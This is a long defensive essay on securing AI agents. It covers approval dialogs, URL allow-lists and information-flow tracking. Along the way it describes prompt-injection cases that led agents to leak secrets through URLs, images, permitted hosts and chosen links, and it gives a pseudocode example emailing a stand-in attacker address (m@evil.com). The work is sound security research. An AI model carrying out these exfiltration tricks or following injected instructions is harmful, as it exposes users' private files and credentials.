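The prototype analyses commands, writes descriptions and binds approvals, but it assumes total mediation and a trusted path to the user rather than implementing them. Total mediation means that the agent can't take any significant action without going through the checker. Without it, an agent could skip the approval, and without the trusted path, it could alter the dialog. Weng didn't test the prototype on commercial agents or with human users. The prototype handled all 22 attacks in a set that Weng designed alongside the analyser, but an earlier version had also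 handled every case in its own test set while missing common abuses.

An executor that makes all of an agent's tool calls already provides much of the mediation that Weng assumes. It also doesn't need a list of trusted programs to identify which argument of `send_email` is the recipient. So the 87.0% figure probably doesn't apply to an agent with a dozen well-described tools. But if one of those tools can run shell commands, the executor has the same problem as the prototype.

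### Endorsing data once or approving each call

An approval permits one call and doesn't change any labels. If the user approves the email to Bob, `address` is still tainted, so the executor will prompt the user again the next time the agent uses it. An endorsement changes a value's label to trusted, so later calls can use the value without another prompt.

Kolluri and colleagues illustrate the difference with an email containing a ten-item to-do list, where each item requires a guarded call. If the planner reads the email without endorsement, its context becomes tainted and the user has to approve all ten calls. If the user endorses the email first, the planner's context stays trusted and the agent can complete the list after asking the user once.

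By answering yes to that single question, the user vouches for every instruction and every value in the email. If an attacker has added an eleventh item that the user overlooks, perhaps in a long quoted message at the bottom, the planner can carry it out with any guarded tool and the executor won't prompt the user. The same goes for a forged account number in one of the ten genuine items. To catch either, the user would have to read the email carefully, and the dialog would have to show all the text that the planner will receive, including anything that a mail program normally hides. With separate approvals, the user sees the eleventh call and its literal arguments before it runs.

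Kolluri and colleagues counted the questions an agent would need to ask when there was no attack, and assumed the user would say yes. They didn't test whether people endorse emails carefully.

#### Approving several calls together

EU payment law offers a compromise between asking for a single confirmation and asking for a separate one for each payment. When a payer approves a batch of payments, the European Commission's regulation requires the authentication code to be specific to the total amount and the payees. The European Banking Authority's *Dynamic linking for batch transactions* adds that the provider must link the code to every payee. The payer must be able to check the list of payees but doesn't have to read all of it.

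An agent could handle the to-do list in the same way. The planner would read the email, accept the tainted context and propose ten calls. The executor would then display all ten with their literal arguments and bind one approval to only those calls. For an eleventh call, or a change to any of the ten, the executor would have to ask the person again.

| Option | Questions | What can run without another question |
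|---|---|---|
| Approve each call | 10 | Only the calls that the user has approved one by one |
| Approve the ten calls as a batch | 1 | Exactly the ten calls on the list |
| Endorse the whole email | 1 | Any guarded call that relies only on the email and other trusted data |

The executor can ask a person to confirm several calls in one batch only if the planner can write them all in advance. If the second call depends on a reply to the first, the executor has to ask more than once. People are also more likely to miss a bad item in a long batch, which is a reason to put new recipients and large amounts at the top.

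#### Endorsing only the address

The user can also endorse a single value. If the hidden variable contains only Bob's address, the user checks one short string and doesn't have to vouch for the rest of the notes.

Even this can permit more than the user intends. The either-rule for `send_email` allows any attachment if the recipient and the context are trusted. Once the user endorses Bob's address, the agent could send him the payroll file later in the same run if the planner misunderstood a request. Kolluri and colleagues deliberately left out blanket declassification, the equivalent of endorsement for confidential data, because whether private data should be released depends so much on the situation. Endorsing a recipient has nearly the same effect as blanket declassification, so the dialog should either explain this or offer an approval for `budget.pdf` alone.

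Saving Bob as a contact extends the endorsement to future tasks. Similarly, under the European Commission's rule on trusted payees, a payer has to authenticate to add someone to the list, but the bank can then skip authentication for payments to that person. This reduces prompts, but a forged payee who gets onto the list can also receive later payments.

### How carefully people read approval prompts

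Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes approval fatigue as people clicking "approve" so often that they stop paying close attention. Studies from 2026 suggest the effect is large, although several involve code or shell commands rather than email addresses.

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports the largest experiment. A research vendor paid 1,053 testers to use a coding agent and, once per session, replaced the text of a permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Testers caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

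Anthropic published these results to justify replacing most prompts with a language model that reviews each action. That model blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers also knew they were in a test environment and not working on their own projects, which may have made them less careful. Even so, 13.6% is very low for obviously dangerous commands, and the decline during a session is consistent with approval fatigue.

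Data from normal use is consistent with this. Anthropic reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code, its coding agent, but reject 39% of the plans the agent proposes. People may read plans more carefully because they are rarer and easier to understand, or plans may give them more to disagree with. In addition, 25% of interactive sessions start in a mode that skips permission prompts.

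*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* examines 290 incident reports about agents and files, and finds that user review contributed to 105. In 80 of these, the agent's actions went through on automatic approval. In 31, the prompt showed a command but not its effect on the user's files. (Some reports had both problems.)

*Habituation at the Gate* (2026) finds a slower change among people who review code from AI agents. Between the earlier and later reviews of 400 repeat reviewers, the approval rate rose from 30.1% to 36.8%, and the share of reviews in which they requested changes fell from 11.2% to 5.6%. Reviewers may have become less careful, but better code could also explain the pattern.

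#### Fewer prompts did not make people more careful

In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) found no benefit from reducing the number of prompts, although this should help if frequent prompts cause fatigue. The 113 participants, who didn't work in software, supervised a simulated day in which an agent proposed 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved or denied every action. Another group first wrote rules that allowed, blocked or required a prompt for broad types of action, such as spending money.

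The group with rules saw 10.9 prompts on average instead of 18. But they approved 66.8% of the out-of-task actions they were prompted about, compared with 40.3% in the group that saw every action. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still had to make most of the decisions themselves.

The comparison is imperfect because people in the rules group saw a prompt only if their own rule called for one, and Yan recruited some of them later without random assignment. The study also included only 18 actions, too few to test how people behave after hundreds of prompts. Still, it suggests that asking fewer questions doesn't necessarily get more careful answers.

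Approval also depended on the type of action. Among those who saw every prompt, 88.2% let the agent make an unrequested call to the airport, but only 20.6% let it post publicly that the user was travelling. People apparently paid some attention to the consequences, which supports stating them in the dialog.

#### Better dialogs helped but took longer

Hossain and colleagues directly tested the content of the dialog. Each of four groups of 20 volunteers used a different interface, and each person judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe.

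| What the dialog showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The description and the exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The above, the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, organised around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Showing the literal values alone reduced unsafe approvals by about 12 percentage points. It couldn't have prevented all of them, because two-thirds of the unsafe requests, such as the one to send `report.csv`, looked harmless without the earlier steps. The benefit of reorganising the facts is less certain. After adjustment, unsafe approvals were 7.9 points lower than with the full log, with a 95% interval from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8.

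#### Little evidence on swapped values

None of these studies tested whether people notice that someone has replaced one plausible address with another. The closest evidence is from Hossain and colleagues, whose participants reviewed some unsafe requests that they could recognise from the call itself, such as a transfer to a prohibited recipient. Participants approved 10 of 40 such requests with the full log and 7 of 40 with the reorganised version. They had the user's restrictions on the screen, and half the requests they judged were unsafe. Bob's user has no list of forbidden addresses to compare with and would rarely see an attack, so these figures may understate how often that user would approve an unsafe request.

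*Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026) provides some indirect evidence. People worked with a computer-using agent on three tasks and could check what it did. Excluding attempts that timed out or hit technical errors, the final result was still wrong in one of nine attempts at one task, five of ten at another and ten of twelve at the hardest. Hossain and colleagues also cite this research as finding that an interface that helped people find errors faster increased their false confidence.

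For a large payment or a very sensitive file, the executor could ask the user to type the recipient's address rather than approve the one from the notes. That would give the user a reason to look up Bob's address elsewhere, but someone in a hurry might copy it from the notes.

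## Checking network destinations

A web address (URL) both names a destination and carries data to it, whereas an email tool takes the recipient as a separate argument. A tool that only reads web pages can therefore send information out. When an agent fetches a page, the site's server receives the whole URL, and OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that websites commonly log the URLs requested from them.

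Suppose Bob's meeting notes link to several budget templates. The planner gives the quarantined model the notes and `budget.pdf`, and asks it for the link to the template that fits best. Text hidden in the notes could make the model return an attacker's URL with the budget's total at the end. The next line of the plan would then fetch that URL.

### The parts of a URL

Almost every part of a URL can hold data:

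```
https://q3-loss.files.example.net:443/budget/48200?for=bob#summary
```

| Part | In the example | Why it matters | Check |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | `http` sends everything unencrypted, and `file` can read the local disk. | Allow only `https`. |
| User name | None | Text before an "@" can look like the host and can carry data. | Refuse any URL that has one. |
| Host | `q3-loss.files.example.net` | It decides which server gets the request, and its first words can be data. | Compare the whole name with the rule before looking it up. |
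| Port | `443` | Another port may lead to a different service on the same machine. | Allow only the expected port. |
| Path and query | `/budget/48200?for=bob` | The server receives both in full. | Check that whoever runs the server may read the data. |
| Fragment | `#summary` | Browsers don't send it, but scripts on the page can read it. | Treat it like the query if a browser opens the page. |

The host needs the most careful check. A rule that accepts any name ending in `example.net` also accepts `badexample.net`, which anyone could register. The executor must also check the name before looking up its numeric address in the domain name system (DNS), because that lookup normally reaches a server chosen by the domain's owner. If the name contained `q3-loss`, the owner could learn those words even if the executor then blocked the connection.

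After looking up a hostname, the tool also has to check the numeric address. An outside hostname can point to an address inside the company's network, where some services trust every request. The tool should then connect to the address it checked, because a second lookup could return a different one.

Servers can also answer with a redirect, which tells the tool to request another URL. The first server has already received the data and can copy it into the new URL, so each redirect needs the full set of checks:

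```
fetch(url, label):
    repeat at most 5 times:
        parts = parse(url)
        refuse if the scheme, user name or port breaks a rule
        refuse if the gate rejects (url, label)        # before any name lookup
        address = look_up(parts.host)
        refuse if address is on a private network
        response = request url from exactly that address
        if response is not a redirect:
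            return response
        url   = response.new_url
        label = label ⊔ (U, L)
    refuse
```

Here `label` combines the labels of the call and the URL. The last line of the loop marks the new URL as untrusted, because an outside server chose it, and keeps any confidentiality limits from the old URL. A rule that accepts only trusted URLs would refuse every redirect, so a developer may want an exception for redirects that stay on the same host.

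### Links and images that load by themselves

An agent can leak data without calling a web tool. Many chat windows display the model's answer as formatted text, and the browser fetches any image in it. If an image's URL contains private data, the browser sends that data to the image's server before the user has read the answer. The executor should therefore treat the model's answer as a sink.

Messaging apps can do the same with ordinary links. Willison (2024) describes how Slack and Discord fetch any link posted in a message to show its title and a preview image. An app that posts to Slack can switch this off for its own messages. The security company PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an agent people can message through chat apps, was exposed to such leaks by default on Telegram.

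An email can leak data even when its recipient is the user. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* includes a May 2026 report about Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which could email the user's own inbox without approval. The messages could contain images from outside servers, so opening a message could send an attacker a link for downloading the user's files without a login. Checking the recipient would not have caught this. An email tool that accepts a tainted body should therefore check the URL of every link and image in it, or convert them to plain text that the mail program won't turn back into links.

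### The Silent Egress experiments

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often a malicious page could make an agent send data out. The agent ran on a small open model, `qwen2.5:7b`, and automatically loaded any page the user mentioned. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The model's context contained a secret, such as an API key (a password for software), and the page told the model to include the secret in a web request.

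The researchers put the instruction in the page's title, its description for search engines, its body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction asked for the secret in one request or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). It never did so in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the summary the user saw was harmless, so a filter on the agent's answers would have missed those attacks.

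Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable, but each request also revealed less. At least one request got out in 185 of 240 runs with split secrets, compared with 238 of 240 with a single request. The first request contained recognisable secret data in 26.3% of the split runs and 96.7% of the single-request runs. The paper gives a lower figure, 15.8%, for the first three requests of the split runs. That can't be right under the paper's definition, since the first three requests include the first, so the exact size of the effect is uncertain.

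Lan and colleagues then tested defences against the simplest attack, which puts the instruction in the page's body and sends the secret in one request. They ran each defence 30 times.

| Defence | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Markers around outside text | 100% |
| A warning in the developer's instructions | 66.7% |
| Markers and warning together | 56.7% |
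| A list of permitted hosts | 0% |
| A filter for suspicious addresses | 0% |
| A filter for words such as "password" | 0% |
| A filter for random-looking values | 0% |

The host list produced the clearest result. The model tried to contact the attacker in every run, and the list blocked every attempt. This was expected because the researchers chose an attacker's domain that was obviously not on the list. Their suspicious-address filter, which they call "redirect detection", looks for raw numeric addresses, certain domain endings and words such as "steal" in the path. They don't describe it following a redirect to its destination.

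The zeros for the last two filters are harder to interpret because these filters had little or nothing to block. With the word filter on, the model attempted a request in only 23.3% of runs, and with the filter for random-looking values on, it never attempted one. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids such values when it is being monitored. However, both filters inspect outgoing URLs, and the paper doesn't describe any way for the model to know they were there.

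#### Why origin is a better test than content

Lan and colleagues argue for tracking where data came from instead of inspecting outgoing data. A four-character piece of a key looks like an ordinary code in a URL, and their filter for random-looking values would ignore it because the filter checks only values longer than ten characters. An attacker can also have the model encode the secret in a form that no word filter detects.

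A label doesn't depend on how the text looks, so each piece of a secret key carries the same label as the whole key. Lan and colleagues propose that the executor also track taint from web pages, and either block any request those pages influenced or ask the user about it. They didn't build this design or test any of their defences against split secrets.

The attack rates are also specific to the set-up. The secret was in plain view, the developer's instructions were minimal, and the researchers tested only one small model. A larger model might resist more often, but the injected instructions were simple, and Lan and colleagues expect better ones to succeed more often. The experiments didn't cover leaks through DNS.

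### Comparing the rules

Developers have tried several rules for deciding which URLs an agent may open without asking.

| Rule | What can pass | How data can still leave | Ordinary work it prevents |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permitted hosts only | Any URL on a listed host | Through a listed host that stores or forwards it | Visiting any other site |
| Only URLs the user typed | An exact match with the user's text | In a URL that the user pasted from an attacker | Following links and search results |
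| Only URLs already public | An exact match in an independent web index | By a choice among indexed URLs | Opening private or very new pages |
| Unlisted hosts count as public channels | Any URL, if it and the call have public labels | Through a wrong label or a listed host | Browsing after the planner has read private data |
| Confirmation of every full URL | Only what the user approves | When the user approves a bad URL | Long tasks without supervision |

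#### Only URLs the user typed

Anthropic applies a looser version of this rule to `web_fetch`, the tool Claude uses to read web pages. Willison (2025) quotes the original documentation, which said that Claude could not construct URLs and could fetch only those that had already appeared in user messages, search results, fetched pages or the results of certain tools. Ordinary code can enforce this rule by comparing strings. The rule blocks the usual attack, in which the model appends private data to an attacker's URL.

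The rule left a gap by also allowing links on pages Claude had already fetched. Willison (2026) reports that the researcher Ayush Paul built a site with a separate link for each letter of the alphabet. The site got Claude to spell out the user's name, home city and employer by following these links. Claude hadn't constructed any of the URLs, but its choice of links revealed the details to the site. Anthropic closed the gap by no longer letting `web_fetch` follow links from pages it had fetched.

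Willison also points out that "user messages" may contain text the user didn't write, because many applications insert documents or emails into them. An executor should therefore compare the URL only with text labeled as trusted.

#### Only URLs already public

OpenAI's rule for ChatGPT depends on whether a URL existed before the conversation. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that collects public web addresses, without access to users' conversations or accounts. If the exact URL is in the crawler's index, the URL probably doesn't contain a particular user's data, and the agent can load it automatically. Otherwise, ChatGPT either has the agent try another website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation.

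OpenAI decided that a list of trusted sites wasn't enough, because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere and a strict list would produce so many warnings that people would learn to click through them. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* says the same mechanism covers page visits in its browser, Atlas, and searches in its Deep Research tool.

OpenAI claims only that this prevents quiet leaks through the URL itself. The page may still contain an injection. Private pages, such as a shared document in the user's company, should never be in a public index, so an agent that works with them will trigger many warnings. OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* says that if a site opts out of OpenAI's catalogue, ChatGPT asks for confirmation of every link to that site.

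An attacker can still leak data through the agent's choice of public URLs, as in the attack on Claude. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* notes that someone with a large blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. Each visit carries `log2(36)`, or about 5.2 bits, and a site with thousands of indexed pages could carry more per visit. The article suggests preventing the agent from requesting the same URL twice in a session. This would make it harder to spell a word with repeated letters, but the agent could still leak 36 bits by visiting some of the 36 pages and skipping the others. The article also warns that OpenAI may not apply the check everywhere, since an earlier version was missing from its Mac and iPhone apps.

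#### Unlisted hosts as public channels

Microsoft suggests treating a displayed link to any unlisted host as a public channel. This means the executor treats the URL's contents as readable by everyone and applies the permitted flow rule as it would to an email. The URL with Bob's budget total has the label `(U, {user})`, so the executor blocks the request. A search for a lamington recipe is allowed if the planner has read nothing private.

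The executor has to check the call's label as well as the URL's. A planner that has read the user's private messages might pick one of 36 links. Each URL is public, but the choice may depend on the messages, and the call's label records that possibility. Checking this label lets the rule block the letter-by-letter attack, which neither of the exact-match rules above blocked in its original form.

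In an ordinary agent, however, the planner can't open any unlisted page after it reads private data. This substantially restricts a research assistant that combines a company's files with web searches. Hidden variables, as in FIDES, would ease the restriction.

#### Confirmation of the full URL

Asking the user about every request would make an agent much less useful. Lan and colleagues add that people usually can't tell whether a request described as a "connectivity check" is genuine. Asking works better as a fallback for the few URLs that another rule rejects.

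The dialog should show the full URL and highlight the data in it. OpenAI's help page gives the example of a user who asks where to buy a car and gets a link ending in `/car_search/London`. The link is useful, but opening it also reveals to the car site where the user lives.

For most agents, the public-channel rule is the best default of these because it uses labels the executor already keeps. A URL the user typed can be an exception, since the user chose both the destination and the data. Hosts on a permitted list are also exceptions, and they need much more scrutiny than they usually get.

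### Why a permitted host is not a permitted recipient

An attacker can receive stolen data through a permitted host if the company that runs it lets anyone open an account, as many do. In January 2026, PromptArmor showed how an attacker could steal files this way from Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that could contact only listed hosts. According to Willison's notes, injected text supplied the attacker's API key and caused the agent to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. The upload was permitted because Anthropic's own API was on the list. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* had described a similar leak through the same file-upload service.

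Willison's collection and Tenable (2025), a security company that found a way around an earlier version of ChatGPT's link check, provide further examples:

| Product | Permitted host | How data could reach an outsider |
|---|---|---|
| Superhuman, an email app | `docs.google.com` | Anyone can create a Google Form there, and it saves the data in a request. |
| Antigravity, Google's coding tool | `webhook.site` | The site records incoming requests for whoever set up the address. |
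| Salesforce's Agentforce | A former Salesforce domain | Its registration had expired, and researchers bought it. |
| ChatGPT | `bing.com` | Bing's result links redirect to other sites. |

#### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches a company's emails and files, had two such incidents a year apart. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes the first. An attacker only had to send the victim an email. When the victim later asked Copilot a question, it could retrieve that email as background, follow the instructions in it, and put private data into the URL of an image in its answer. The browser then loaded the image without a click.

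Three of Microsoft's defences failed. A classifier for prompt injections missed the email because the email's instructions seemed to address a human reader. A filter that removed outside links from Copilot's answers missed some ways of writing them. The third defence, a content security policy, limited the hosts from which the browser could load images. It permitted Teams and SharePoint, and both had services that would fetch another URL on request and so pass the data to the attacker's server.

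The list also used wildcards. A wildcard that permits every host under `sharepoint.com` permits the sites of all SharePoint customers, which can include an attacker's. The attack through SharePoint required the victim to accept an invitation to the attacker's site, but the one through Teams required no action from the victim.

Microsoft patched the flaw in 2025. According to SC Media, the company said that nobody had exploited it in real attacks and that customers didn't need to do anything. An executor with labels could have stopped the leak without recognising the injection or the odd link. The answer drew on an outsider's email and on private files, so it was both untrusted and private, and the gate should have blocked any image in it from a server that others could use.

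#### SearchLeak

The list that Ravia published also permitted `bing.com`. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (June 2026) described an attack on Copilot's enterprise search that used that domain. The victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft site, and Copilot followed instructions in the link's search text. It then searched the victim's mailbox and put an email's subject line into an image URL.

Microsoft's code converted such images into harmless text, but only after Copilot had finished its answer. By then the browser, which displayed the answer as it arrived, had already requested the image. The request went to Bing's image search, which fetched the attacker's URL from Bing's own servers, where the browser's list of permitted hosts did not apply. Microsoft rated the vulnerability critical and fixed it. Varonis recommends cleaning the text before the browser displays it and reviewing every permitted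 host that fetches URLs supplied by others.

An executor that trusts everything in the user's message would also have had difficulty stopping SearchLeak, because the text came from a link but arrived in the user's input box. Such text needs an untrusted label, as does a document that the user pastes in.

#### Writing a narrower list

Each entry on a host list should name both the host and the account or storage area that may receive data. For a file-upload service, the executor can add the user's credentials itself and reject any that the agent supplies, so an upload can't go to somebody else's account. For SharePoint, the entry should name the company's own site, without a wildcard.

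The developer can then give each entry a set of readers, as with an email's recipients. The company's SharePoint site might have all employees as readers, while a public code library would have everyone. Services that forward requests or let strangers collect data should count as public, whoever runs them. Redirects on a trusted site are also a risk. Oasis Security's *Claude.ai Prompt Injection to Data Exfiltration* describes an attack that used one on `claude.com`. Domains expire and services gain new features, so the developer has to review the list regularly.

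### Where to put the check

| Place | What it can check | What it cannot see |
|---|---|---|
| Executor | The literal URL, its label and the user's request | Redirects, name lookups and a tool's hidden connections |
| Tool | Each redirect and the numeric address | Labels, unless the executor passes them on |
| Network proxy | Every connection from the agent's machine | Labels, and usually the path and query of an encrypted request |
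| Chat window or browser | Images and links as they load | Labels, and requests that the agent's tools make |

Of these, only the executor has the labels by default, so it should make the main decision. It can pass the tool a short permit specifying the acceptable hosts and readers. The tool then checks each redirect against the permit, or returns the new URL to the executor for another decision.

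This works only if the tool makes no connections beyond those it declares. Qu and colleagues' requirement of tool integrity rules out undeclared connections, but checking a call's arguments can't enforce it. The same problem arises with a tool that runs shell commands, since a short script can contact any server. A network proxy, a program through which all the machine's traffic must pass, can block these connections whatever the tool does.

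The proxy has to handle name lookups too, or a script could leak data through DNS without making a connection. To read the path and query of an encrypted request, the proxy has to decrypt the traffic, which gives it access to passwords and other private data. Even then, it can't distinguish a public number from a salary without the executor's labels. Lan and colleagues suggest that network controls limit the rate of requests and compare them across a session, which might reveal a secret sent in pieces.

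A proxy on the agent's machine can't check requests for images in a chat window, because the user's browser makes them. The application should filter the agent's answer with the same parsing code it uses to display it. In the EchoLeak attack, the filter failed to detect some links that the display code rendered. A content security policy in the browser is a useful second defense if its list of allowed domains is short.

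When Bing or Teams fetched the attacker's URL, the request came from Microsoft's servers, so neither the victim's browser nor a proxy on the victim's network could block it. A defense could stop the data only before it reached the permitted host.

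## Leaks that pass every argument check

The gate checks the values in a tool call and what the planner had read when it chose the call. But information can also travel through what the agent does or fails to do, such as sending an email, stopping with an error or taking one branch of its plan instead of another. These implicit flows don't copy any value, so the gate may not find a suspicious label.

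### The branch that never ran

An executor can catch the simplest implicit flows. GAAP catches the one in the plan that emails Ana only if a salary is high. CaMeL similarly applies a condition's label to everything inside the branch, so it blocks an example from Garby and colleagues in which an agent emails an attacker only if a customer's account balance is above a threshold.

The leak comes back if the branch only sets a variable and the email goes out later. Security researchers have known the trick since the 1970s. Buiras, Stefan and Russo (2015), in *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems*, give a four-line version, and Garby and colleagues adapt the idea to CaMeL. In outline:

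```
1  rich = True
2  tmp  = True
3  if account.balance > threshold:  tmp = False
4  if tmp:                          rich = False
5  if rich:                         send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| 1–2 | `rich` and `tmp` are True and public. | `rich` and `tmp` are True and public. |
| 3 | The assignment runs. `tmp` becomes False and secret. | The executor skips the assignment. `tmp` stays True and public. |
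| 4 | The executor skips the assignment. `rich` stays True and public. | The assignment runs. `rich` becomes False and stays public. |
| 5 | The condition is public, so the email goes out. | No email goes out. |

In both runs `rich` ended up with a public label, and its value showed whether the balance was above the threshold. The executor raised a label only when an assignment ran inside a secret branch, which happened once, to `tmp` in the first run. In the second run `tmp` kept its public label, although it stayed True only because the balance was low. *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues, 2015) explains that a monitor that tracks one run covers only the branches that execute. It can't detect what the other branches would have assigned.

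To use this leak, an attacker needs a plan with this shape and a way to see whether the email arrives. CaMeL's planner writes the plan from the user's request alone, so the attacker can't ask it for these five lines. But a harmless request can also lead to a plan with this flaw. For example, the user might say, "Send Bob the contract at his work address, or at his home address if the notes say he has changed jobs."

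```
to = "bob@work.example"
if quarantined_model("Has Bob changed jobs?", notes):  to = "bob@home.example"
send_email(to=to, attachment=contract)
```

If the notes contain a line about Bob's new job, the executor assigns his home address to `to` inside a tainted branch, and the gate blocks the email. If they don't, `to` keeps his old work address and its trusted label, and the email goes out. An attacker can therefore get the contract sent to Bob's old employer by deleting that line.

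#### Three repairs and what they cost

Buiras and colleagues sort the known repairs into three groups.

| Repair | What the executor does | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Analysis before the run | Counts the assignments in every branch, including those that may not run | Needs the whole plan in advance, in a language simple enough to analyse |
| No-sensitive-upgrade | Stops the run if a secret branch tries to change a public variable | Stops harmless plans, even when nothing uses the variable afterwards |
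| Permissive upgrade | Allows the change, marks the variable as partially leaked, and stops only if a later branch depends on it | Stops fewer harmless plans, but needs the extra mark and more complicated rules |

GAAP uses the first repair and taints everything between a branch and the point where its paths rejoin. LLMbda uses the second. In the plan about the balance, LLMbda's rule would stop the run at line 3 whenever the balance was high, so the email would not be sent.

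For Bob's contract, the second and third repairs stop the run that changes the address but still let the default address through. Only an analysis of both paths would taint `to` in either case and block both emails.

A coarser option is to keep a single context label for the whole program, as in LIO, the programming library that Buiras and colleagues extend. Reading a secret raises the label on everything that follows, so branches need no special treatment, but label creep returns.

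An agent's conversation with a model can leak a secret the same way `rich` does. In a test by Garby and colleagues, a program tells the model that `x` is false, then, only if a secret is true, tells it to set `x` to true, and finally asks for `x`. LLMbda labels the conversation as well as the variables. It stops this run at the second message because a secret condition would change a public conversation.

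### What a refusal reveals

An observer who sees a program stop at line 3 learns that the balance was high. Most information-flow systems allow a leak of about one bit per run, but it becomes serious if an attacker can repeat the run freely.

#### Retries outside the tracked program

The untracked retry loop around CaMeL's interpreter allows such repetition. Each new attempt starts with no recorded dependence on private data, even though the planner may write it in response to an error that depended on that data.

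Suppose the secret is a four-digit PIN, which has 10,000 possible values. A program that fails only if the PIN is 5,000 or more rules out half of them. The next program can split the remaining half, and 14 attempts are enough to identify the PIN, because 2^14 is 16,384. The attacker has to influence what the planner writes from one attempt to the next and observe which attempts fail. CaMeL censors the error messages that go back to the planner, which makes the attack harder but isn't formally guaranteed to prevent it.

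Moving the loop inside the tracked program closes the channel, but a failed attempt then taints the next one, and the final plan may be too tainted to call any guarded tool. Garby and colleagues avoid this with a rehearsal, in which the agent writes and repairs its program against an artificial copy of the world that contains no real secrets or attacker's text. The agent uses the real tools only once the program works. This also prevents a retry from making the same payment twice. However, the rehearsal doesn't flag label violations, so a plan that passes it can still break a rule on real data.

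A simple limit on attempts costs less. It leaves the channel open but caps how much can pass through it.

#### Learning from a denial

In an ordinary agent, the planner reads the refusal and can pass on what it learns from it. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) gives the example of an injected instruction to read `/etc/shadow`, the file where Linux stores password hashes. The policy denies the call. If the error is "permission denied" rather than "file not found", the planner can infer that the file exists. It then sends an email saying so. The email contains nothing from the file, and no tool result connects the two calls, so ordinary taint tracking does not flag the email.

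One denial reveals little, but an attacker can probe many files or services and send out the pattern of refusals, which shows what the system protects. The attacker can also have the agent first turn the pattern into a number with a calculator tool, so that the final message looks unrelated to the refusals. Both attacks require the planner to read the attacker's text, so they work against an ordinary agent, or against FIDES after the planner has inspected an untrusted variable.

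Chinaei's proposed defence, the Agentic Reference Monitor, keeps a graph of tool calls, including denied ones, and the data passed between them. It automatically links each denied call to the next call with a "counterfactual edge", and anything computed from that next call inherits the link. Before a sensitive call runs, ordinary code checks whether any path in the graph leads back to a denial.

The monitor can't detect whether the denial influenced the planner, so it treats the denial as if it had. A harmless email that follows a denial can therefore fail the check. This rule may also be too narrow. If the monitor links the denial only to the next call, an attacker could have the agent make one irrelevant call after the denial and then send an email that doesn't use that call's result.

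In Chinaei's tests, the monitor blocked three attacks that a simpler tracker missed: a denial leak, an attack involving taint passed through several calls, and one involving a result that mixed trusted and untrusted fields. Each decision took less than a millisecond. These three chosen scenarios show that the mechanism works as intended, but they don't measure how much legitimate work it would block.

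Two simpler measures solve part of the problem. The executor can check the path before it touches the file system and return the same message whether or not the file exists. It can also give every error the label that a successful result would have had, as GAAP does. The second measure matters more when the rule depends on private data. If the gate refuses to send `budget.pdf` to Bob because he isn't among its readers, the planner can learn from the refusal that Bob may not read the file.

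### What FIDES guarantees and what it leaves out

Costa and colleagues don't claim that FIDES stops every implicit flow. They show that taint tracking of this type can enforce explicit secrecy together with safety, where safety means that a forbidden call never runs. Two definitions are needed here:

- **Explicit secrecy:** if the agent's steps stay the same, changing the secret data changes nothing that an outsider sees.
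- **Noninterference:** changing the secret data changes nothing that an outsider sees, even though the agent may now take different steps.

Explicit secrecy and noninterference differ when a secret decides whether a call happens, as in the plan that emails Ana only if a salary is above 100,000. Suppose the email would contain a public web page, which FIDES keeps in a hidden variable. Because the page has a public label, the permitted flow rule allows the email even after the planner has read the salary. This satisfies explicit secrecy because nothing in the email depends on the salary, but it violates noninterference because Ana would get no email if the salary were 100,000 or less.

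A developer could close this gap by letting the agent send a message only to people who are allowed to read both the message and everything the planner has read. After reading the salary, the agent could then send messages only to the user.

Full noninterference would rule out many tasks that people want an agent for. An agent that checks a private calendar and declines an invitation reveals something about the calendar to the sender. Noninterference for integrity would require that untrusted data never affect a trusted action, so an agent couldn't add a meeting to the calendar because an email asked for one. A rule that forbids all such information flows can't separate the harmful ones from the ones users want. Chinaei adds the practical objection that the influence passes through the model's internal reasoning, where the executor can't follow it.

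Explicit secrecy is still worth having because it covers cases where an agent copies a document or a password into a message. Costa and colleagues argue that explicit secrecy and safety together are enough to stop most practical prompt injections. But explicit secrecy gets weaker as the agent bases more of its decisions on data, since each decision can reveal information about that data. Narisetty and colleagues reviewed seven systems and found that confidentiality and implicit flows were the weakest areas across the field.

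### What LLMbda proves

LLMbda has a noninterference theorem. Garby and colleagues had to adapt noninterference in two ways, because a language model's answers are partly random and because the interpreter sometimes stops a run.

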